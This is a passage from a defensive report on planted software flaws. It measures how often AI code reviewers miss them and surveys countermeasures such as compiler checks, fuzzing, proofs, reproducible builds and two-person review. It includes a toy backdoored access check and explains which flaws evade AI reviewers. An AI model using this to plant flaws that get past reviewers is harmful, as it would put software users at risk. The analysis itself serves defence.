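Missed by both, if independent:   0.143 × 0.092      ≈ 1.3%
```

The second reviewer removed more than two-thirds of the remaining flaws. Nearly 50 of the 1,088 flaws still got past both reviewers, whereas multiplying their miss rates gives an expected total of about 14.

One reason is that some flaws were hard for every reviewer. Multiplying the two reviewers' miss rates separately for each row of the table raises the expected share missed by both from 1.3% to about 2.1%. The rest of the gap suggests that the two reviewers also found the same flaws difficult within each row.

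A third reviewer helped less than one might hope. The three together missed 28 of the 1,088 flaws, when they would have missed only one or two if their errors had been independent.

The choice of second reviewer also matters, because two models may miss the same flaws. On changes that resembled genuine repairs, Sonnet 5 and Opus 4.8 missed mostly the same ones, with agreement of 0.69 on a scale where 0 is chance level and 1 is perfect agreement. Both are Claude models from Anthropic and ran in the same agent, which may explain the overlap. In the long runs of changes, agreement between any two reviewers was at most 0.24, and even a second Claude model caught some flaws the first had missed.

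### The right verdict for the wrong reason

The reviewers failed in different ways. When Sonnet 5 or Opus 4.8 missed a flaw, it approved the code about four times out of five. In 79 of its 100 misses, GPT-6-Sol rejected the change but repaired the wrong part, and in 70 of those it neither named nor edited the place where the flaw was.

CyberDual counts these cases as misses because the proof of concept still worked. A project that threw out every rejected change would have stopped them, and at most 21 of the 1,088 flaws (2%) would have got past GPT-6-Sol and at most 125 (about 12%) past Sonnet 5. But a project can hardly discard a hundred good changes every time a reviewer objects to something. And if the reviewer names the wrong problem, the contributor can fix that problem and submit the planted flaw again.

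Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*, measured how often this happens. Their benchmark, MalPR-Bench, contains 89 pull requests with a known vulnerability and 50 without one. Before testing any reviewer, they wrote down what a review would have to include to show an understanding of each flaw.

They tested CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial AI reviewer, on 31 of the vulnerable pull requests. It blocked 24 but identified the real flaw in only 16. The gap was wider among the 12 that came from real projects and contained previously unknown vulnerabilities, where it blocked ten and identified the flaw in four. In one case, a new feature didn't check ownership, so a user in one project could open saved work from another. CodeRabbit flagged only how the program displayed secrets on the user's screen, and fixing that would have left the vulnerability in place.

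Missing checks were the hardest to diagnose, because no line of code is visibly wrong. CodeRabbit blocked nine of the 14 pull requests with missing checks but identified the flaw in only three. It identified none of the seven flaws that a reviewer could confirm only by reading files outside the change, compared with 16 of the other 24. The static analysis tool CodeQL covered 21 of the 31 cases and identified none of the flaws.

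Access to the whole project does not guarantee that an AI reviewer will find a planted flaw. Chen and colleagues ran a Codex agent twice on each of three pull requests where the evidence of the flaw was in a similar but unconnected part of the program. The agent blocked the change in four of the six runs but did not identify the flaw in any of them.

Chen and colleagues also built their own reviewer, PRGuard, which first proposes a specific vulnerability and then looks for evidence in the project's code. Using a DeepSeek model, it blocked 22 of the 31 and identified 22 flaws, including nine of the 14 missing checks. The comparison somewhat favours PRGuard, because it had already found the 12 flaws in real projects in an earlier run with another model. PRGuard was also inconsistent, changing its verdict in up to a quarter of the 44 reviews that the researchers repeated.

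Most of the flaws in MalPR-Bench came from incomplete or partly reversed security fixes, and the 12 from real projects were apparently accidents. MalPR-Bench labels the flaws malicious, but most were not disguised to fool a reviewer. A skilled saboteur's flaws might be harder to diagnose.

### One real alarm in 560

An AI reviewer that examines every change will also raise false alarms. CyberDual did not measure how often its reviewers rejected harmless changes. Its catch rates alone are not enough to judge whether the reviewers are useful, because a reviewer that rejected every change would also catch every planted flaw.

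As with static analysis, even a low false alarm rate causes trouble when sabotage is rare. Suppose that one change in 10,000 is malicious, and that a reviewer catches 90% of malicious changes but also raises an alarm on 5% of the others. Nobody knows the true share of malicious changes, so the first figure is only an assumption. In 10,000 changes, the reviewer would raise:

```
Correct alarms:      1 × 0.90 = 0.9
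False alarms:    9,999 × 0.05 ≈ 500
Share correct:   0.9 / 500.9  ≈ 1 in 560
```

A project receiving 50 changes a day would get two or three false alarms daily and one malicious change about every 200 days. By the time a malicious change arrived, the maintainers would probably have stopped taking the alarms seriously. For half the alarms to be correct, the reviewer could wrongly flag no more than about one in 11,000 harmless changes.

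A second reviewer can reduce or increase false alarms, depending on how the project uses it. Suppose both reviewers have a 5% false alarm rate and their false alarms are independent. If the project blocks any change that either reviewer flags, it will block nearly 10% of harmless changes. If both must flag a change, it will block only 0.25% of them, and about one alarm in 30 will be correct. But by CyberDual's figures, Sonnet 5 and GPT-6-Sol both catch only about 80% of planted flaws. Reviewers that miss the same flaws may also flag the same harmless code, in which case requiring both to flag a change would help less.

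Researchers have published little evidence on real false alarm rates. On the 50 harmless pull requests in MalPR-Bench, PRGuard wrongly blocked five (10%) with GPT-5.5 and four (8%) with DeepSeek. With a sample this small, five out of 50 is compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 3% to 22%. These pull requests were also complete security repairs, so they don't show how often PRGuard would block an ordinary change. CodeRabbit blocked none of the six harmless pull requests it reviewed.

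The AI Cyber Challenge included a small test of the same ability. The organisers sent the finalists 13 security warnings, five of which were false, and asked which were valid. Two systems that relied mainly on a language model's judgement got ten and nine right. Three others confirmed a warning only when they had an input that caused a matching crash. This made them more cautious, but they could not dismiss the false warnings, and the winning system still matched crashes to two of the false ones.

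The check of Anthropic's scanner, where only one finding in 97 was invalid, does not contradict this calculation. It measured the share of alarms that were wrong, while the 5% is the share of harmless changes that set off an alarm. Old software also contains many accidental vulnerabilities, so a scanner has far more to find there than someone looking only for sabotage.

Accidental vulnerabilities also make alarms in code review more likely to be correct. Suppose that, besides the one malicious change in 10,000, one change in 100 contains an accidental vulnerability, and that the reviewer catches 90% of both kinds. About one alarm in six would then point to a real flaw, which would give a maintainer good reason to check the alarms.

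## What protects software when nobody spots the flaw?

Some planted flaws will get past both human and AI reviewers. A project can still make such flaws harder to write, to get through automatic tests and to deliver, and it can limit the damage if one reaches users. Most of these measures work on the code or the finished program, so they apply unchanged when an AI model wrote the code, but rules about who may approve a change need more thought.

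### Making the flaw harder to write

Many contest entries depended on a few well-known traps in C. *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (Wheeler, 2020) examined the vote-counting programs from Horn's 2004 contest to find out how many would have survived simple precautions. One of the 41 published programs contained no attack, so Wheeler located the malicious lines in the other 40. This was difficult even with Horn's notes on each trick, and four of the notes were wrong or incomplete.

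Wheeler then chose five countermeasures:

- compiling the program with gcc, a widely used compiler, with many of its warnings switched on
- running it with AddressSanitizer, a tool that detects reads and writes outside the memory set aside for them, at the cost of roughly halving the program's speed
- forbidding most macros
- forbidding the names `l` and `O`, which look like the digits 1 and 0
- using an editor that colours comments differently from code, and reformatting the program so that no code can follow a comment on the same line

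Together, the five exposed 30 of the 40 programs (75%). Gcc's check for misleading indentation should have caught one more but missed it because of a bug. Wheeler thought six of the other nine looked odd enough to make a reviewer suspicious. Of the last three, one used the wrong table's size and so filled in only part of a table, another converted numbers to the wrong type, and the third checked twice for a lower-case "n" instead of checking for "n" and "N".

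Both of Horn's winners were among the 30, and gcc gave a relevant warning for each. Wheeler had entered two programs in the contest himself. A gcc warning exposed one, while the other got past all five countermeasures, although he considered its repetitive code suspicious.

The 75% probably overstates how well the same measures would work against new tricks, because Wheeler chose them after studying the old ones. He acknowledges this and says he only wanted to show that a few simple measures can often work. He ran gcc on every program but mostly judged the other measures by reasoning about the code. He also didn't measure how many false alarms the measures would raise in honest programs. The entrants couldn't have tested their programs against his version of gcc, which came out 15 years after the contest. An attacker today can try every public tool before submitting code, so Wheeler suggests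 keeping the details of some checks private, though an open-source project would find that difficult.

Compiler makers add checks after well-known accidents. Neither compiler Langley tried in 2014 warned about Apple's repeated `goto fail`, but gcc's standard set of warnings now covers misleading indentation. Language designers can go further and remove a trap. Solidity's developers used the entries in its 2017 underhanded contest to find weaknesses in the language and its compiler.

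The largest change of this kind is the move to memory-safe languages such as Rust, which normally prevent a program from reading or writing memory it should not touch. *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025) reports that memory errors fell below 20% of Android's vulnerabilities for the first time in 2025. Google (2025) says such vulnerabilities are 1,000 times less dense in Android's Rust code than in its C and C++ code. Almost all of these are presumably accidents, but a saboteur trying to plant a memory error would face the same obstacles. Rust changes also spend 25% less time in code review (The Hacker News, 2025), which is welcome if reviewers no longer need to look for memory errors, but less so if they also spend less time looking for other flaws.

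Rust programmers can mark a block of code as "unsafe" to do things the compiler would otherwise reject, though the mark at least shows reviewers where to look. A saboteur can also choose a flaw unrelated to memory, such as a missing check on who owns a record. Theori often found this mistake in programs written by AI, so a memory-safe language would leave much of the risk in such programs untouched.

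### Getting past the tests

Fuzzing catches many planted flaws, including more than half of those in DARPA's final, but it is poor at finding a backdoor that opens only for one particular input. If that input is four bytes long, there are 2³² possibilities, and a fuzzer that tries 1,000 random ones a second would need about 50 days on average to hit the right one. With eight bytes, it would need more than 500 million years.

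Modern fuzzers improve on these odds by recording which parts of the program each input reaches, then varying the inputs that reached something new. If the program compares the four bytes one at a time, the fuzzer can find them one at a time, in about 1,000 attempts. This method does not help against the xz backdoor, which required a valid digital signature, because a partly correct signature gets no further than a completely wrong one.

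The fuzzer also needs some sign that the program has gone wrong, and by default it looks for a crash. A vote counter that gives Bush extra votes does not crash. Wheeler therefore recommends combining fuzzing with assertions, which are conditions in the code that must always hold. For example, an assertion could require the candidates' votes to add up to the number of ballots. But Horn gave bonus points for keeping that total right, so the better entries would have satisfied it.

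Measuring test coverage, the share of the code that the tests run, can reveal a different kind of trick. Wheeler's more suspicious entry ran separate code on election day. Ordinary tests would have passed on any other date, but a coverage report would have shown that they had never run a large part of the program.

Formal verification replaces samples with a mathematical proof that the program meets a specification for every possible input. The proof is only as useful as the specification. This made-up access check lets people read their own documents, but also lets user 4107 read everybody's:

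```
may_read(user, document):
    return user == owner(document) or user == 4107
```

A tester who picks a few user numbers at random will almost certainly miss the exception. A proof has to cover user 4107 along with everyone else, but whether it fails depends on what the programmers set out to prove. They might choose one of these specifications:

- Specification A: the owner of a document can always read it.
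- Specification B: the owner of a document can always read it, and nobody else ever can.

| Who asks | Program's answer | Specification A | Specification B |
|---|---|---|---|
| The owner | Yes | Met | Met |
| User 4107, who is not the owner | Yes | Met | Violated |
| Any other user | No | Met | Met |

The program meets specification A, so a valid proof exists even though the backdoor is still there. The program violates specification B, so no proof is possible, and many verification tools would report user 4107 as the counterexample. Programmers easily write specifications like A because they tend to think about what a program should do for its users before they think about what it must never do for anyone else.

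Real access rules are also more complicated than specification B. People share documents, administrators need access, and support staff may need it temporarily. Each exception makes the specification longer and gives a saboteur another place to hide a flaw. Someone who could edit the specification might add a reasonable-sounding rule for support staff, then take a support job to gain access. The weakness in Dual EC, the random number generator with a possible master key, was in the standard itself, so proving that a program followed the standard would also have proved that it contained the weakness.

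Proofs have also taken a lot of work. The team behind seL4, a small operating system kernel, needed about 20 person-years to verify fewer than 10,000 lines of C. AI models could greatly reduce that work, and nobody would have to trust the model that wrote the proof, because a small program can check each step. People would still have to read the specification as suspiciously as they would read untrusted code.

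### Delivering what the reviewers approved

Someone can alter a program after reviewers have read it and fuzzers have tested it. Reproducible builds make this easier to detect. The project publishes its source code and a record of the tools and settings used to build it. Anyone can then compile the source under the same conditions and compare the result with the released file, byte for byte. If an intruder altered the program on one build machine, as at SolarWinds, the released file would not match the files other people built.

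Builds that nobody has tampered with often fail this comparison too. *In a Big Move to Linux Security, Debian Makes Reproducible Builds Mandatory* (Rudra, 2026) lists ordinary causes such as a time stamp in the program, an identifier generated during the build, or files stored in whatever order the disk returned them. Developers have to remove these differences before they can treat a mismatch as a warning.

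In May 2026, Gevers (2026) announced in *bits from the release team* that new packages could no longer enter Debian's testing edition, which becomes the next release, unless others could reproduce them. The rule also blocks updates that make an existing package unreproducible. Rudra reports that, among packages that work on every type of processor, 23,731 passed at the time and 414 failed, a pass rate of 98.3%. In a follow-up, *Re*, Gevers (2026) explained that maintainers can ask for exceptions and that Debian runs two kinds of test. One deliberately varies the conditions to provoke differences, while the other tries to reproduce the files that users install, which he considers more important for users.

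Other collections of software are further behind. IzzyOnDroid, a collection of Android apps, reached reproducible builds for two-thirds of its apps in June 2026, according to Reproducible Builds (2026), the project that promotes the method. Python packages do much worse. In a study of 12,180 popular releases, summarised in the project's July report (Reproducible Builds, 2026), only 15.4% and 19.1% of the rebuilds made with two different tools matched the published files exactly. The researchers wrote a program that ignores harmless differences, and it accepted 60.2% and 78.9% of the rebuilds that started from equivalent source. This makes the check more practical, but somebody has to decide which differences are harmless, and an attacker would try to make a malicious change look like one of them.

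Old software can also become impossible to check. In another study in the July report, researchers tried to rebuild 18,904 versions of Android apps that had matched when F-Droid, an app store, published them. They rebuilt 83%, and 94% of those still matched, so about 78% of the total passed. Missing dependencies caused most of the failures, so it makes sense to check a release soon after it appears, while its dependencies are still available.

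Comparing independent builds cannot expose a flaw in the source, because every build will include it. The comparison would not have exposed the xz backdoor either, although the attacker hid part of it outside the repository. Debian built xz from the release archive, which contained the altered build file, so rebuilding Debian's package would have reproduced the backdoor. A compiler like Thompson's could also infect every rebuild in the same way, unless somebody checks it with a second compiler.

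Detecting the altered xz file requires an earlier comparison, between the release archive and the repository. The July report describes VCAligner, which compares contents to match a released package to its source commit. Developers usually rely on version labels for this, but among 2,984 Python packages the labels failed in about 15% of cases, which would have left more than 10 million commits to inspect. VCAligner reduced that to under 65,000. Lucas Nussbaum has announced Debaudit, a service for Debian that tests whether the source package itself is faithful, according to a Reproducible Builds report copied on longform.social.

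Signed provenance also connects a program with its source. The machine that builds the program records which source it used and how, then signs the record so that nobody can change it unnoticed. A user's installer can reject a package whose record names the wrong source. SLSA, the set of supply-chain guidelines, gives the example of The Great Suspender, a browser extension whose publisher released software that was not built from the source code the publisher claimed. This check needs only one build, whereas reproducible builds need at least two. However, everyone has to trust the machine that signs, and an intruder who controls it may be able to sign a false record.

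### Requiring a second person

Two-person approval is a safeguard applied before software is built. In November 2025, SLSA (2025) announced version 1.2 of its voluntary guidelines, which added a set of levels for source code. The highest level, described in SLSA's *Source*, requires two trusted people to agree to every change to a protected branch, the line of development that leads to releases. They can be the author and a reviewer or two reviewers. If the author edits the change during review, the reviewers must approve the final version, which prevents someone from adding a flaw after getting approval.

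The two-person review rule stops one insider, or an intruder with one stolen account, from acting alone. It does not help if the second person misses the flaw, and an attacker who controls two trusted accounts can approve their own work. Small projects also have difficulty following it. Collin could have followed it at xz only by giving somebody else authority over the project.

SLSA defines a trusted person as a human, so a coding agent cannot be one of the two trusted people required. If a developer asks an agent for a change and submits it, another person still has to approve it. In the GitHub projects that Agarwal and colleagues studied, about two in five of the agents' pull requests and about one in five of the human-written ones would have failed this requirement.

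SLSA does let a project exempt a "trusted robot", such as an automatic dependency updater, from the rule, but only if no single person can influence the robot's identity or code. A coding agent seems a poor candidate, since a stranger may be able to change what it does by writing instructions in a bug report.

### Limiting the damage

Developers who assume some flaws will get through can limit what an attacker gains from them. Under the principle of least privilege, each program or user gets only the access needed for the job. A sandbox can enforce this while the program runs. For instance, a program that opens image files rarely needs the network or the user's other documents. If an attacker takes it over with a malicious image, a good sandbox keeps them from reaching much beyond that image.

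Removing unnecessary connections between programs can help in the same way. If systemd had stopped loading the compression library sooner, the xz attacker would have lost the route into OpenSSH.

Other protections make a flaw harder to exploit without removing it. In 2025, developers found a possible memory error (CVE-2025-48530) in unsafe Rust code in an Android component that reads images. According to Better World Technology, the way Android allocates memory would have prevented an attacker from using the error to run code remotely.

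These protections don't help much when the flawed code needs the access it abuses. A hospital's records system has to read patients' records, so a sandbox can't stop it from showing them to the wrong person if a permission check is missing. Dual EC leaked its secrets through random numbers that the program was supposed to send. An attacker may also target the sandbox itself, as Jia Tan did by adding a full stop to the code that quietly disabled Landlock.

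Once somebody discovers a flaw, fast updates shorten the time attackers have to use it. The EU's Cyber Resilience Act, which became law in 2024, requires manufacturers to provide security updates for products with digital components. Most of its obligations are due to apply from December 2027. But updates also deliver planted flaws. SolarWinds' customers got the backdoor by installing a signed update, and the xz backdoor did little harm partly because most distributions had not yet adopted the new version.

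A project can handle this conflict by installing security fixes at once and waiting before it adopts other new versions. A six-week wait would have avoided the xz backdoor, but not the one in SolarWinds, which went undetected for more than eight months after its release. Waiting also works only if somebody else uses the new version first. Freund found the xz backdoor because he was running a test version of Debian, and if everyone had waited, it might have gone unnoticed for longer.

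### Maintainers and commit rights

All these measures give maintainers more work. They have to read the compiler's warnings, investigate builds that do not match and release the fixes. The maintainers of many widely used projects are volunteers, and they already receive more vulnerability reports from AI tools than they can handle. Exhausted maintainers are also easier to pressure into accepting help from a stranger, as happened to Collin.

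Companies that depend on a project can pay its maintainers or lend them staff, and some governments now fund open-source work too, as Germany does through its Sovereign Tech Agency. Money might have given Collin the time to review the new releases or the confidence to ignore the complaints, though it would not have helped him judge whether Jia Tan was honest. Paid staff can be corrupt too, but their employer at least knows who they are.

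Projects can also grant authority in smaller pieces. Much of Jia Tan's visible work was documentation and translation, which does not require permission to publish releases. A project could let a helpful newcomer manage bug reports or one part of the code, while an automatic system builds the release archives directly from the repository. In the xz case, such a system would have left out the altered build file unless Jia Tan had also committed it to the repository, where other people could have seen it. An attacker could still earn every permission eventually, but would need more time and have to convince more people.

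Checking contributors' identities before granting commit rights would have made it harder for Jia Tan, whom nobody appears to have met, to get them. But it would also exclude honest volunteers who have good reasons to stay anonymous, including some who live under the governments most likely to attempt such an attack. An intelligence service could also pass the check by using a real programmer with genuine identity documents.
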